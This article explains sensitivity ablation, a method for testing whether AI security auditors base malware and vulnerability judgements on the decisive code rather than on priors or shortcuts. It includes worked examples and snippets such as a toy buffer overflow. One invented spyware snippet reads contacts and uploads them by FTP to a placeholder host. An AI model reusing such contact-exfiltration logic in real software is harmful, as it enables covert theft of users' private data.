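# How sensitivity ablation tests whether a model's security judgements rest on the code

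## What the test asks and the terms it needs

Sensitivity ablation is a test for language models that judge whether code is dangerous. The tester replaces the code ranked most relevant to security with lower-ranked code, keeping the input the same size, and measures how far the model's score falls. Zheng, Qian and colleagues (2026) describe the test in *Is "Knowing It's Malicious" Enough?* as one part of MalEval, a framework for evaluating models that audit Android malware. The test is useful because a model can judge code correctly for reasons that have little to do with the code.

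Take Maikspy, a spyware program that Zheng and colleagues use as their running example. One of its functions, `Alarm.onReceive`, belongs to a group of functions that read contacts and text messages and upload files over FTP. Simplified, and with invented names, the relevant part might look like this:

```java
public void onReceive(Context ctx, Intent intent) {
    List<Contact> people = readContacts(ctx);
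    File dump = writeToFile(people);
    ftp.upload("files.example.net", dump);
}
```

A model that correctly calls this app spyware may have traced the contacts from the address book to the upload, or it may call nearly every app spyware once a detector has flagged it. The answer is the same in both cases, and so is the accuracy, the share of answers that are right.

The MalEval results include something close to the second case. GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model, kept the "malicious" verdict on 96.57% of the real malware, but it cleared only 36% of the harmless apps that Zheng and colleagues had added as simulated false alarms. Their collection held 230 malicious apps and 25 harmless ones, so a program that printed "malicious" every time would be right about 90% of the time. Some of GPT-4o-mini's correct verdicts may well rest on the code, but we can't tell which ones from the verdicts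 alone.

### Security judgements and how to score them

A security judgement is any claim a model makes about danger in code. It can be a yes-or-no verdict, a category such as "spyware", or a statement that a particular function steals contacts.

Vulnerability detection usually examines one function at a time, looking for mistakes in otherwise legitimate software that an attacker could exploit. Malware detection is the task of deciding whether someone built a whole program to do harm. Malware auditing starts after a detector flags an app. The auditor states what the app does, points to the code that proves it, and withdraws the flag if the evidence does not support it. Sensitivity ablation comes from auditing, where a claim without supporting code is of little use to an analyst even if it is true.

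Most scores for these tasks build on precision and recall. Precision is the share of a model's claims that are correct. Recall is the share of what the model should have found that it did find. Suppose an expert's report on an app lists five malicious operations, and a model reports four operations, three of which match the expert's. Precision is 3/4 = 0.75 and recall is 3/5 = 0.60. F1 is the harmonic mean of the two:

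F1 = 2 × 0.75 × 0.60 / (0.75 + 0.60) ≈ 0.67

F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and recall. This mean lies nearer the lower of the two, so F1 penalises a model that does well on one and badly on the other. The penalty is fairly mild, as the example of a detector that flags everything will show.

### Decisive code, priors and shortcuts

Decisive code is the code without which the correct security judgement would not be justified. A short C example from Suneja, Zheng and colleagues (2020), in *Probing Model Signal-Awareness via Prediction-Preserving Input Minimization*, makes the idea concrete:

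```c
int a = 99;
int b = 57;
char arr[69];
if (b < a) {
    b = 78;
}
arr[b] = 'X';
```

The array has 69 slots. Since 57 is less than 99, `b` becomes 78, and the last line writes past the end of the array. Nobody could justify calling this a buffer overflow without seeing the array's size, the assignment to `b` and the final write.

Suneja and colleagues then shortened the condition from `b < a` to `b`. The program still overflows, because C treats any non-zero number as true. But a neural network with an F1 of 99 out of 100 on this kind of code changed its answer from "buggy" to "non-buggy", so its answer depended on more than the overflow. They argue that a model can separate buggy from healthy code perfectly by using sample length or variable names, if those happen to differ between the two groups in the data.

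Later detectors have the same problem. *Evaluating Line-level Localization Ability of Learning-based Code Vulnerability Detection Models* (2025) measured which lines affect the output of transformer-based detectors and found that lines without a vulnerability significantly influenced "vulnerable" predictions.

A prior is what the model would answer before reading the code at hand. A shortcut is a cue that goes with the right answer in the test data but is not the reason the answer is right. *VISION* (2025) gives a pair of functions that both use a variable called `mode`. The harmless function fills it from a secure internal source, while the vulnerable one fills it with unchecked user input. A detector that has come to associate `mode` with danger would be right about the vulnerable function and wrong about the harmless one. So a shortcut does depend on the input, just on the wrong part of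 it, whereas a prior needs no input at all. (Some shortcuts lie inside the decisive code, and removal cannot isolate those.)

### Right answers that come from elsewhere

A high base rate is the simplest source. If most apps that reach an auditor are malicious, then "malicious" is a good guess about an app containing this line:

```java
WorkManager.getInstance(ctx).enqueue(syncJob);
```

The line schedules a background job with WorkManager, Android's standard tool for this, as many harmless apps do. Zheng and colleagues describe a benign app that a model reported as a trojan, partly because it mistook WorkManager for a channel to an attacker's server. A strong prior towards "malicious" is one plausible cause of that error. The same prior would produce a correct verdict whenever the line appeared in real malware.

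A model's prior can favour either verdict, vulnerable or safe. In *Calibration Without Comprehension*, Zibaeirad and Vieira (2026) gave models vulnerable Linux kernel code and its repaired versions. A 7-billion-parameter DeepSeek-R1 model flagged 96.1% of the vulnerable samples from before 2025 and judged 4.5% of the repaired ones safe. GPT-4.1-mini flagged 5.7% and judged 93.6% safe. Both were about 50% accurate, roughly what random guessing would achieve, because the first model called most samples vulnerable and the second called most safe.

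These are small models, but the same problem affects larger ones and F1 scores. Cichoń and Dmitruk (2026), in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model*, consider a detector that flags functions at random with probability p. On a set that is half vulnerable and half repaired, its F1 is 2p/(1 + 2p). If it flags every function (p = 1), its F1 is 0.67, the same as that of the model above that got three of its four claims right. They also tested GPT-5.2 on 1,000 pairs, each containing a function before and after its vulnerability was fixed. GPT-5.2 flagged both versions in 82% of the pairs and judged both correctly in 11%. Its F1 was 0.672, the highest of the seven commercial and large open models on that set.

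Memory of a known sample is harder to pin down. Consider one line from the Linux kernel function `ingress_init`, as it stood before the fix for CVE-2024-41010 (a CVE number identifies a publicly recorded vulnerability):

```c
tcx_miniq_set_active(entry, true);
```

The call looks fine on its own. The flaw is visible only in another file, which declares `miniq_active` as a true-or-false value, although the kernel needs a number to count several users. This causes a use-after-free, meaning that the program keeps using memory it has already released. A model that sees only `ingress_init` and reports the use-after-free cannot have worked it out from that code. The published fix may have been in its training data, or it may have guessed, since this kind of flaw is common in the kernel.

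*RealVuln* (2026), which tests code scanners on 26 public GitHub repositories, lists as a limitation that memorised vulnerabilities could inflate recall. *OpenAnt* (2026) raises the same concern about Juliet and the OWASP Benchmark, two openly available test suites. However, direct attempts to find this effect have mostly failed. Zibaeirad and Vieira found that models had no consistent advantage on vulnerabilities that also appeared in their fine-tuning data. They attribute this partly to the training set, which held no usable copy of the vulnerable function for 84% of the nominally overlapping samples.

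Djiré, Barr and colleagues (2026), in *Learned or Memorized?*, tested for memorisation differently, by making small changes to the inputs of eight code models. They assumed that memorised answers would break abruptly, while understood ones would degrade slowly. On CVEFixes, a widely used collection of vulnerability fixes, their measure stayed below 0.1, compared with up to 0.8 on some other benchmarks. This is decent evidence against rote recall but weaker evidence that the models were reading the code, because a model that gives every function the same answer would also barely react to small changes. The question remains open for Android malware. Zheng and colleagues could not rule out memorisation there because few recent samples have both a downloadable app and an expert report.

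Metadata can also supply the answer. An Android app carries a manifest, a file that declares its name and components:

```xml
<manifest package="com.mybank.update.free">
```

The (invented) name looks suspicious and an analyst would probably notice it, but the name itself does not steal anything. When Zheng and colleagues added the package name, version, declared components and signing details to the input, the share of harmless apps that Gemini-2.5-Pro cleared rose from 47.8% to 83.3%, and GPT-4o-mini's share rose from 36% to 68%. The models' evidence scores changed little, or moved in different directions. The researchers added all the metadata at once, so the experiment doesn't show how much the package name contributes by itself. Signing details can be fair evidence of who published an app, but metadata becomes a shortcut when the question is what the code does.

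The last source is an artefact of the dataset, and the best-documented example is function length. In *Mitigating fix reversal*, Bian, Li and colleagues (2026) divided the training functions of PrimeVul, a standard vulnerability dataset, into five groups by length. Only 0.27% of functions in the shortest group were vulnerable, compared with 9.38% in the longest. Ranking functions by length alone detected vulnerabilities about as well as CodeBERT, a pretrained code model they had fine-tuned for the task.

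They also caught the shortcut at work in a single function, a ZIP parser from the SerenityOS operating system that omits several length checks. In place of the missing checks they inserted comments containing no words, as long as the real fix. In outline:

```c
/* ---------------------------------------- */
read_file_name(buffer);   /* still no length check */
```

The comments do not change what the program does, but adding them raised CodeBERT's estimated probability that the function was vulnerable past the alarm threshold. The function was vulnerable, so the alarm was correct, but punctuation in the comments had triggered it. The properly repaired function, which is also longer, triggered the alarm too. *Cyber-JEV* (2026) likewise traces false alarms to function length, and also to the coding style of the repository a function comes from.

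### Why removing code is informative

If a judgement rests on certain code, removing that code should change the judgement. Suppose the tester replaces the contact-stealing functions in the Maikspy input with functions that draw a settings screen, then runs the model again. A model that relied on the upload should no longer report that contacts leave the phone. A model that calls every flagged app spyware will give the same answer, because it wasn't using the removed code. So will one that relied on the package name, if that name is still in the input. Replacing the removed code matters because of cases like the ZIP parser. If the input only got shorter, the answer might change because of the input's length.

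The verdict is a coarse measure here because spyware often contains more than one incriminating function. A model that bases its judgement on the code could lose the most incriminating function and still answer "spyware". A correct verdict can also rest on bad reasoning. In *Beyond True or False* (2026), Llama-3.1-8B flagged over 80% of the vulnerable code with a basic prompt, but its recall fell below 10% when a correct answer also required sound reasoning. MalEval's removal test therefore compares evidence F1, which is calculated by matching the individual pieces of evidence in a model's report against those in an expert's.

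### Three meanings of "sensitivity"

In statistics, sensitivity is the true-positive rate, or true positives divided by the sum of true positives and false negatives. It is also called recall, which is the safer term here. A detector that flags everything has perfect recall, but its verdict would not change if someone removed the decisive code.

MalEval's Sensitivity Index (ΔS) measures how much a model's evidence F1 drops when its input is reduced. It is the evidence F1 on the full input minus the evidence F1 on the reduced input. Djiré and colleagues also use "sensitivity" for a model's response to changed input, but they treat a strong response as a bad sign because they make changes that a human would ignore. In sensitivity ablation, a strong response is desirable because the removed material ought to matter.

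A function's sensitivity score is a rough estimate of how likely the function is to take part in security-relevant behaviour, such as handling private data or calling privileged operations. A high score does not mean that the function is malicious, since a legitimate messaging app also has to read contacts. In MalEval, the model under test produces the scores, which are used to rank the functions.

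## Choosing which evidence to remove

The tester has to decide which items count as most important before removing any code. The same model can show a large drop on the same app under one ranking and almost none under another, so the ranking largely determines what the drop measures. A tester has five practical sources for the ranking.

| Source of the ranking | Cost | Requirements | Question the test then answers |
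|---|---|---|---|
| The tested model's own scores | Almost nothing, if the model already scores items while summarising them | Only the tested model | Does the model depend on code that it rated highly itself? |
| A second model's scores | One scoring pass, which serves every tested model | A model outside the comparison | Does the model depend on code that another model rates highly? |
| Lines changed by the fixing commit | Little computing, some manual checking | A vulnerable–patched pair | Does the model depend on the lines the developers changed? |
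| Program slices | Program analysis of every sample | A known dangerous operation, and code the analysis tool can process | Does the model depend on the code that feeds the dangerous operation? |
| Measured influence | Dozens or hundreds of extra runs per input | Usually, the probability the model gives to a fixed text | Did the ranking find what moves the model? |

### What matters to the truth and what matters to the model

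*ContextCite* (Cohen-Wang, Shah and colleagues, 2024) calls a passage corroborative if it supports or implies a statement, and contributive if it caused the model to produce the statement. In Maikspy, the function that uploads contacts corroborates the claim that the app steals contacts, whether or not a particular model used it. In the benign app that a model reported as a trojan, the WorkManager call probably contributed to the model's claim, but it doesn't support it.

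Removing corroborative code tests whether the model uses the right code, unless the same facts survive elsewhere in the input. Removing contributive code mostly tests the ranking, because the tester has already established that those functions affect the output. Removing them will change the output whether the model relies on variable names or follows the contacts to the server.

Removing the most influential function from an input can raise Evidence F1. If that function is harmless but led the model to a false claim, the claim disappears when the function is removed, which raises precision and F1. Ranking functions by influence can therefore produce a negative Sensitivity Index even for a model that depends heavily on its input.

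### When the model ranks its own evidence

MalEval uses the tested model's own sensitivity scores. These are the model's estimates of which functions matter to the correct answer, and they may not match the functions that affect its output. The scores take little extra work to obtain because the model produces them while writing the function summaries, which it has to write anyway.

The trouble is that ΔS then depends on two abilities, ranking the functions and using them. Take an invented app whose input holds 300 function summaries, five of them decisive. The expert report lists five malicious operations, one for each decisive function. Models A and B read these functions equally well. Each reports all five operations, plus five false ones that have nothing to do with the decisive code. In counts, F1 is 2 × correct claims / (all claims + operations in the expert report), so both models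 start at

F1 = 2 × 5 / (10 + 5) ≈ 0.67

Now the tester removes each model's top 30 items, the same 10% share that MalEval uses, and refills the input with harmless functions. Model A had all five decisive functions in its top 30, so it loses all five correct claims, its F1 falls to 0, and ΔS is 0.67. Model B had only one of them in its top 30. It is left with nine claims, four of them correct, so its F1 is 2 × 4 / (9 + 5) ≈ 0.57 and ΔS is about 0.10. Model A looks nearly seven times as dependent on the code, although both models rely on it equally.

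The refill can even raise the score. A MalEval input holds at most 300 functions, while the average app in the collection has about 2,565 reachable ones (functions the program could actually run), so the model's ranking determines which ones are included. Suppose model C ranks one decisive function in its top 30, two more between places 31 and 300, and the last two at places 305 and 320. Its full input contains only three of the five, and its F1 is 2 × 3 / (8 + 5) ≈ 0.46. When the tester removes the top 30 and adds places 301 to 330, the input loses one decisive function and gains two. F1 rises to 0.57, and ΔS is −0.11. Someone who saw only ΔS might conclude that the removed code was useless to the model, when the model had ranked its evidence badly.

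Zheng and colleagues knowingly use ΔS for both abilities. They list it as the measure for "function prioritization" (finding the security-critical functions), and they also read a large drop as a sign that the model reasons from code instead of from priors. One of their follow-up experiments suggests that the two abilities can differ considerably. When they removed information about each function's callers and callees (the functions that call it and those it calls) from the summaries, Gemini-2.5-Pro's evidence F1 fell by about 17%, from 24.24% to 20.20%, but its ΔS fell by about 40%, from 11.21 to 6.75 percentage points. Either a worse ranking or weaker reliance on the most important functions would produce that pattern, and self-ranking cannot separate the two explanations.

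### Rankings that come from outside the model

Using a second model's scores to choose which functions to remove avoids this confound, because every tested model loses the same functions. If the second model ranked three of the five decisive functions in the top 30, models A and B would both drop from 0.67 to 0.33. The drop would understate both models' reliance on the code equally, because two decisive functions would remain in the input. The second model should also choose which 300 functions enter the full input and write their summaries, so that the tested models start from the same evidence.

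The second model should preferably not be closely related to any tested model. In *AttriBoT*, Liu, Kandpal and Raffel (2024) compared how strongly each passage of an input influenced models of different sizes. The scores from models of 1 to 8 billion parameters correlated highly with those from a 70-billion-parameter model of the same family. The study measured influence in question answering, so it's only suggestive here. But if related models also agree about which code is important, a ranking from one family could cause larger drops in that family's models than in others.

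Neither of these sources guarantees that the top-ranked code is decisive. For vulnerabilities, the fixing commit offers something closer to ground truth. The file server Pure-FTPd once compared strings with a function like this one, shown here in simplified form:

```c
int pure_strcmp(const char *s1, const char *s2) {
    return pure_memcmp(s1, s2, strlen(s1) + 1);
}
```

If `s1` is longer than `s2`, the comparison runs past the end of `s2` (CVE-2020-9365). The developers fixed this by replacing the single line in the function's body with four lines that use the shorter of the two lengths. The original line is a good candidate for removal, since nobody could justify the claim of an overrun without seeing which length the function passes to `pure_memcmp`. The loop that does the reading is also decisive, but it is in `pure_memcmp`, which the fix didn't change.

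Other commits are less helpful. Lekssays, Mouhcine and colleagues (2025) point out in *LLMxCPG* that patches often include unrelated refactoring, so a tester who removes every changed line may take out a lot of harmless code. Some fixes only add lines. The ZIP parser in SerenityOS, for example, was vulnerable because it lacked length checks, so there is no check to remove, and the tester has to use judgement to pick the operation that the check should have protected. Malware has no fixing commit. The nearest equivalent is the expert report, but MalEval does not label individual functions as malicious, so someone would have to trace each reported operation back to the code by hand.

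Program slicing automates part of that tracing. A slice is the part of a program that is relevant to one chosen point, the slicing criterion. A backward slice collects the statements that affect the values used at that point (data dependencies) and the conditions that decide whether the program reaches it (control dependencies). For the small overflow program with the 69-slot array, the backward slice from the final write is the entire program, because the write uses the array and `b`, the value of `b` depends on the `if`, and the `if` compares `b` with `a`. In a realistic function, the slice leaves out most lines.

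Choosing the criterion is the hard part. A fixed list of dangerous functions such as `strcpy` misses the wrappers that developers write around them. If the criterion is an `if` condition, the slice may include the whole block beneath it, relevant or not. Lekssays and colleagues therefore trained a language model to write queries for Joern, a program-analysis tool. The queries search for paths from a risky value to a risky operation, such as from a length variable to the call that adds that many bytes to a network buffer. Their system then finds the variables that interact with the path and slices backwards from all of them. This shortened one 85-line function to 18 lines, and across their datasets it cut the code by 67.84% to 90.93%.

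A detector reads these slices, whereas sensitivity ablation removes the slice and keeps the rest. The test then checks whether the model's claim depends on the code that feeds the dangerous operation. Its result is only as reliable as the criterion used to choose the slice. When Zheng and colleagues gave DeepSeek-R1 slices built around sensitive Android calls in place of function summaries, its F1 for malicious behaviours fell from 61.27% to 37.75%. They suggest that such slices miss malicious logic that isn't tied to a sensitive call. Removing the same slices would leave that logic in the input. The slicing tool also failed on some apps, which a tester would have to exclude or rank in another way.

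### Measuring influence by leaving items out

The remaining source asks nobody's opinion about which code is important. It changes the input and records what happens to the output. In the simplest version, leave-one-out attribution, the score of item i is

score(i) = log p(response | full input) − log p(response | input without item i)

The response is what the model gave for the full input, and p is the probability the model assigns to producing that text again. An input with 300 items requires 301 passes through the model, one with everything present and one with each item left out.

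ContextCite gets by with far fewer passes because it leaves out many items at a time:

1. The model answers from the full input, and the tester chooses a statement to explain, such as "the app sends contacts to a remote server".
2. The tester creates random versions of the input, keeping or dropping each item with a probability of one half.
3. For every version, the tester records the probability p that the model gives to the original statement. The model doesn't write a new answer.
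4. The tester converts each p to its logit, log(p / (1 − p)). Probabilities stop at 0 and 1, while logits have no limits, and this suits the next step better.
5. A linear regression learns to predict the logit from which items were present. Cohen-Wang and colleagues use LASSO, a kind of regression that sets many weights to zero.
6. The weight of each item is its score.

A weight of 3 on Maikspy's upload function would mean that including the function raises the logit by 3, other things being equal. That would raise the statement's probability from 0.50 to about 0.95.

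In one ContextCite example, the input had 98 sentences, and 32 random versions were enough. This works because a statement usually depends on only a few sentences. The number of versions needed grows in proportion to the number of influential sentences, but only with the logarithm of the total number. On question answering and news summaries, ContextCite with 32 versions matched or outperformed leave-one-out and three other methods at finding the sentences whose removal made the original statement less likely. None of the tests involved code.

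Some of its known weaknesses would affect code reports directly. A sentence in the answer may depend more on an earlier sentence than on the input. For example, a model that has written that someone was born in 1990 can work out the person's age without using the input. Likewise, the verdict in a malware report follows from the evidence listed above it, so the tester should compute influence for the individual evidence claims and not for the verdict. Deleting one item can also change what another means, as when a pronoun loses the noun it refers to or a variable loses its definition.

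Later methods mostly reduce the computation needed. Liu and colleagues store intermediate results that different versions of the input share, screen large blocks before small ones, and use a smaller model of the same family in place of the large one. Together, these changes made leave-one-out attribution more than 300 times faster in some settings. *Learning to Attribute with Attention* (2025) trains a single predictor on the model's attention weights, which record how strongly each generated token draws on each earlier one, so the tester doesn't have to fit a new regression for every example. In *Sketching Language Models for Context Attribution*, Liaw, Mehta and colleagues (2026) estimate all the leave-one-out scores with a number of runs that depends on the error the tester will accept, not on the input's length. Their guarantee assumes that the output changes smoothly as items gradually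 fade out, and the method needs access to the model's internals. They tested it on Llama-3.2-1B, a very small model.

With many commercial models, a tester can't obtain the probability of a given text, so they would have to generate a new report for each version. DeepSeek-R1 took 1.45 minutes per report in MalEval. At that speed, 301 reports would take more than seven hours per app, and 32 would take about 46 minutes.

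If a model already knows a fact, removing the passage that states it has little effect, so the passage gets a low influence score even though it supports the answer. Trinh, Zhu and Szyller (2026), in *How Context Attribution Handles What the Model Already Knows*, tested this with 1,987 multiple-choice questions about cybersecurity. Each came with six passages, three of them from text on which the researchers later fine-tuned the model. They ranked the same passages by influence before and after the fine-tuning, using four methods that included ContextCite and AttriBoT. Agreement between the two rankings was between 0.34 and 0.56, on a scale where 1 means identical. A model that recognises a malware family from its training data could likewise give low influence to the functions that prove its judgement correct, and a test that used influence to choose what to remove would leave them in place.

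Influence is therefore a poor basis for the main test, but it is useful alongside it. If the tester uses a fix or an expert's annotation to identify the decisive code and removes it, influence scores can then show which other items were affecting the model's judgement.

### How large an item, and how many to remove

The size of the evidence items limits how useful any ranking can be. Removing single lines is precise, but a line rarely means much alone, and deleting one often breaks the rest of the function. When Cohen-Wang and colleagues scored single words instead of sentences, their regression predicted the effect of removals less well. They suggest this is because a statement depends on many words at once, and words depend on one another more strongly than sentences do. Lines of code are probably like words in this respect.

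Functions are easier to swap and to match with an expert's claims, but removing one takes out harmless lines along with the decisive ones. Slices keep a value, its checks and its use together, but two slices can share lines, so removing one may damage the other. Summaries save space. In the DeepSeek-R1 comparison, summaries of all the selected functions took up about 18,700 tokens on average, while the decompiled code took about 52,200 and still covered only 28.37% of the items. However, a MalEval summary describes a function together with its callers and callees, so an upload may still appear in a neighbour's summary after the summary of the function that performs it has been removed. For most tests of malware auditing, the function is a sensible unit, provided the tester also checks its callers and callees. For a vulnerability inside a single function, a slice makes more sense.

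A tester who is unsure how much to remove at once can start with large pieces, then test smaller ones within them. Liu and colleagues found that a paragraph's influence was almost perfectly correlated with the summed influence of its sentences (R = 0.97). They could therefore score ten paragraphs, keep the two most influential, and score sentences only within those. For an Android app, the equivalent would be to score classes first, then the functions inside the highest-scoring ones. The correlation may be weaker there, because functions in different classes often work together.

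The share to remove is harder to set in advance, because the number of decisive functions differs between apps and nobody knows how well the ranking has placed them. Testing only one share can mislead, as experiments by Trinh and colleagues show. They measured how much of the accuracy gained from the passages was lost when they removed the top-ranked ones. With Llama 3 8B and a ranking method called TracLLM, removing the top passage out of six eliminated 75% of the gain, while removing the top two or the top three eliminated only 38%.

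It is better to remove several shares in turn and plot the drop against the share. The table below gives the drop at each share for models A and B from the invented example. Model A ranks the decisive functions 2nd, 5th, 9th, 14th and 27th, and model B ranks them 12th, 48th, 95th, 160th and 240th. Model D ignores the code and writes the same plausible spyware report every time, which earns the same F1 of 0.67. The refill contains no decisive code.

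| Share removed | Items removed | Drop for A | Drop for B | Drop for D |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 3 | 0.10 | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| 5% | 15 | 0.48 | 0.10 | 0.00 |
| 10% | 30 | 0.67 | 0.10 | 0.00 |
| 20% | 60 | 0.67 | 0.21 | 0.00 |
| 40% | 120 | 0.67 | 0.33 | 0.00 |
| 80% | 240 | 0.67 | 0.67 | 0.00 |

At a 10% cut, model B looks much more like D than like A. By 80% it matches A, because both have lost all the decisive code, however they ranked it. The left end of the curve mainly reflects the quality of the ranking, and the right end reflects how much the model uses the input. Real curves will be less tidy, since large cuts need a large refill and leave the model with a very different app to read.

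Each new share requires only one more report, because MalEval already has a summary for every reachable function. At DeepSeek-R1's speed, the six shares in the table would add about nine minutes per app to a pipeline that takes 31 minutes.

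## Refilling the input to the same size

Deleting the top-ranked functions removes the evidence and also shortens the input. If the score then falls, the tester can't tell which change caused the drop.

Input length alone can change a model's judgement, as it did for the detector that Bian and colleagues fooled with blank comments. If a model scores longer code as more suspicious, it would flag fewer apps after any deletion, even of harmless code. A shorter input can also make the task easier. If 30 of 300 summaries are removed, the model has less irrelevant material to process and may find the remaining evidence more easily, which would hide part of the loss caused by the deletion.

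Zheng and colleagues refill the input, which keeps its length roughly constant. Here is an invented input for Maikspy, with five summaries instead of 300. Only the name `Alarm.onReceive` comes from the real app.

```
1. Alarm.onReceive    Reads contacts and text messages, then uploads them by FTP.
2. SmsStore.readAll   Copies every stored text message into a list.
3. Main.onCreate      Opens the first screen and sets the timer for the upload.
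4. Prefs.load         Reads the saved colour theme and font size.
5. Thumbs.trim        Deletes old thumbnails when storage runs low.
```

The tester removes the first two items and refills their places:

```
1. Dates.format       Turns a date into text in the user's language and region.
2. Layout.resize      Fits the buttons to the width of the screen.
3. Main.onCreate      Opens the first screen and sets the timer for the upload.
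4. Prefs.load         Reads the saved colour theme and font size.
5. Thumbs.trim        Deletes old thumbnails when storage runs low.
```

Both inputs have five items and almost the same number of words. But the reduced input still mentions an upload in item 3 by mistake, so part of the evidence remains.

### What the new material does to the score

The refill is ordinary code that the model processes along with the rest of the input. It can distract the model from the remaining evidence, prompt a false claim, or supply evidence that the full input lacked. Two studies of vulnerability detection give some idea of how large these effects are. Neither removed any evidence from the function being tested, so they show the effect of extra material by itself.

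*Vulnerability Detection with Interprocedural Context in Multiple Languages* (Lira, Fonseca and colleagues, 2026) tested four commercial models on 509 vulnerabilities from ReposVul, a dataset built from the commits that fixed them. The models had to judge whether a function was vulnerable after seeing it alone, with its callers, or with its callees. On C code, GPT-4.1 Mini's accuracy was 75.6% with the function alone, 68.8% with callers and 51.0% with callees.

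That figure overstates the effect somewhat, because some functions had no callees to add. The 75.6% covers 356 C functions and the 51.0% only 204. The researchers also compared the models on exactly the same functions, across C, C++ and Python together:

| Model | Alone → with callees | Functions | Alone → with callers | Functions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 99.2% → 97.9% | 237 | 96.8% → 97.7% | 221 |
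| Gemini 3 Flash | 100.0% → 95.5% | 157 | 99.3% → 96.4% | 140 |
| GPT-4.1 Mini | 73.8% → 54.0% | 237 | 70.6% → 69.2% | 221 |
| GPT-5 Mini | 89.6% → 84.2% | 222 | 87.8% → 77.0% | 213 |

After correction for multiple comparisons, only GPT-4.1 Mini's 20-point fall with callees and GPT-5 Mini's 11-point fall with callers were statistically significant. The same kind of added code can lower one model's performance a lot and barely affect another's. This complicates comparisons of ΔS between models, because part of the difference may come from how much the refill affects each model.

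The study can't show whether the added code lowered accuracy through its content or its length. In C, adding callees roughly doubled the average prompt length, from 2,367 to 4,785 tokens. Every function in the study was also vulnerable, so accuracy equalled recall and would fall in the same way if a model became more inclined to answer "safe". Harmless refill might also make a model more inclined to give that answer.

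In *Representation Matters*, Stoltman, Tang and Cai (2026) come closer to separating length from content. They tested one model, Qwen3.6-plus, on 107 C and C++ functions from PrimeVul, 55 vulnerable and 52 safe. The model received the source code, a text version of graphs that describe the code's structure, or both. The graphs record syntax, the order of execution and the dependencies between statements.

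| Input | Accuracy | Average tokens |
|---|---|---|
| Graphs only | 74.4% | 5,973 |
| Graphs and source code | 69.4% | 12,938 |
| Source code only | 53.5% | 10,767 |

Stoltman and colleagues call the fall from 74.4% to 69.4% context dilution, meaning that added material makes the relevant evidence less prominent. The averages are weak support for this explanation because the two groups contain different combinations of graphs. Adding source code to a prompt with only the syntax graph lowered accuracy from 72.1% to 69.3%, and adding it to a prompt with only the dependence graph lowered accuracy from 69.0% to 65.7%. The researchers ran each prompt once and advise caution about differences of one to three points. A length limit also removed more worked examples from the longer prompts, which may have lowered accuracy.

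One of their cases is more convincing. A function in FreeRDP, a remote desktop program, contains this check:

```c
if (Stream_GetRemainingCapacity(s) / 12 < NumberOfPipes)
    return NULL;
MsPipes = calloc(NumberOfPipes, sizeof(...));
```

The check limits `NumberOfPipes` before the program allocates memory, so the function is safe. The model classified it as safe with all six graph-only inputs, but as vulnerable with all three inputs that added source code. The added text included a different routine that computes a buffer size as `16 + NumberOfPipes * 20`, and the model identified that calculation as the flaw. These prompts were at most 26,008 characters long, under the limit of 50,000, so the limit cut nothing from them. A refill item like that routine could lower evidence F1 by prompting a false claim, even if the removed code had never affected the model's judgement.

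Extra code can also help. On the 23 cases of double free, in which a program releases the same memory twice, graphs with source code reached 76.2%, compared with 64.6% for graphs alone. An example that Lira and colleagues take from libgit2, a library for working with Git repositories, shows how this can happen. The function `git_pkt_parse_line` can report success while setting a pointer to NULL, meaning that it points to nothing. That may be deliberate. The flaw is in the caller, which uses the pointer without checking it:

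```c
/* pkt is not checked for NULL */
if (pkt->type == GIT_PKT_ERR) {
```

If the full input holds only the first function and the refill adds the second, the model gains the missing half of the evidence. The tester should read the refill before running the test, at least for a sample of apps. They can then use random-removal runs to estimate how much the swapping itself lowers the model's performance.

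### The objection that the input is unnatural

A model may also fail on a reduced input because the input is out-of-distribution, meaning it is unlike anything in the model's training data. If that is why the score drops, the drop is a poor measure of how much the model relied on the evidence.

The objection became prominent in work on image classifiers. In *A Benchmark for Interpretability Methods in Deep Neural Networks*, Hooker, Erhan and colleagues (2018) replaced a random 90% of each image's pixels with the average colour. The accuracy of a ResNet-50 classifier on ImageNet, a standard collection of labelled photographs, fell from 76.68% to 0.5%. But new models trained from scratch on images altered in the same way reached 63.53%. The remaining pixels still held most of the useful information, so the original classifier probably failed more because the altered images looked strange than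 because pixels were missing.

They proposed a test called remove and retrain, or ROAR:

1. Rank the pixels of every training and test image by estimated importance.
2. Replace the top-ranked share with the average colour.
3. Train new models from scratch on the altered training images.
4. Measure their accuracy on the altered test images. A larger fall means a better ranking.

Hooker and colleagues used a small artificial dataset to show what retraining corrects. Only four of its 16 features were informative, and they removed the 12 useless ones first, following a completely wrong ranking. Accuracy fell quickly without retraining, which made the ranking look good, but when they retrained the model, accuracy stayed level until all 12 were gone.

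Hase, Xie and Bansal (2021) reject part of this argument in *The Out-of-Distribution Problem in Explainability and Search Methods for Feature Importance Explanations*. They say that, for one trained model, the drop clearly happened because replacing the features changed the prediction. Asking what the model would have done if it had trained on such inputs means asking about a different model.

Saying that the replacement did the damage is true, but it doesn't help much with sensitivity ablation, because the tester wants to know whether the damage came from removing the old material or adding the new.

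Hase and colleagues give another reason to worry about unnatural inputs. Suppose someone trains BERT, an early language model, to label single words as positive or negative, then replaces a word with a mask token that never appeared in the training examples. The model's answer to the mask can't come from those examples, so it depends largely on the model's starting point and on chance during training. Any importance score calculated from that answer depends on them too. But people who read the score expect it to reflect what the model learned from the data.

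Their remedy is to add training examples with random tokens removed. This made models up to 22.9 percentage points more accurate on inputs with missing tokens, but an average of 0.7 points less accurate on ordinary ones. On BoolQ, a set of yes-or-no questions about short passages, they used a random search to find the tokens whose removal did the most damage. Removing those tokens lowered the ordinary models' confidence by 55.8 points, but the specially trained models' by only 31.6. A good part of the larger drop may therefore have come from the unfamiliar input.

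Unlike sensitivity ablation, retraining from scratch shows whether a new model could learn the task from what is left. Suppose a tester removes the upload functions from every spyware sample and retrains. The new model might learn to recognise spyware by the functions that ask for access to contacts, and score as well as the original model, even if the original depended entirely on the uploads. Hooker and colleagues acknowledge that the retrained model is not the one whose features they ranked.

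Retraining also has biases. *Fine-Grained Neural Network Explanation by Identifying Input Features with Predictive Information* (2021) found that two methods with smooth importance maps did slightly better on ROAR than a third. When the researchers smoothed the third method's maps, it did about as well as the other two. *On Pitfalls of RemOve-And-Retrain* (2023) likewise reports a persistent "blurriness bias" in ROAR and a related measure, ROAD.

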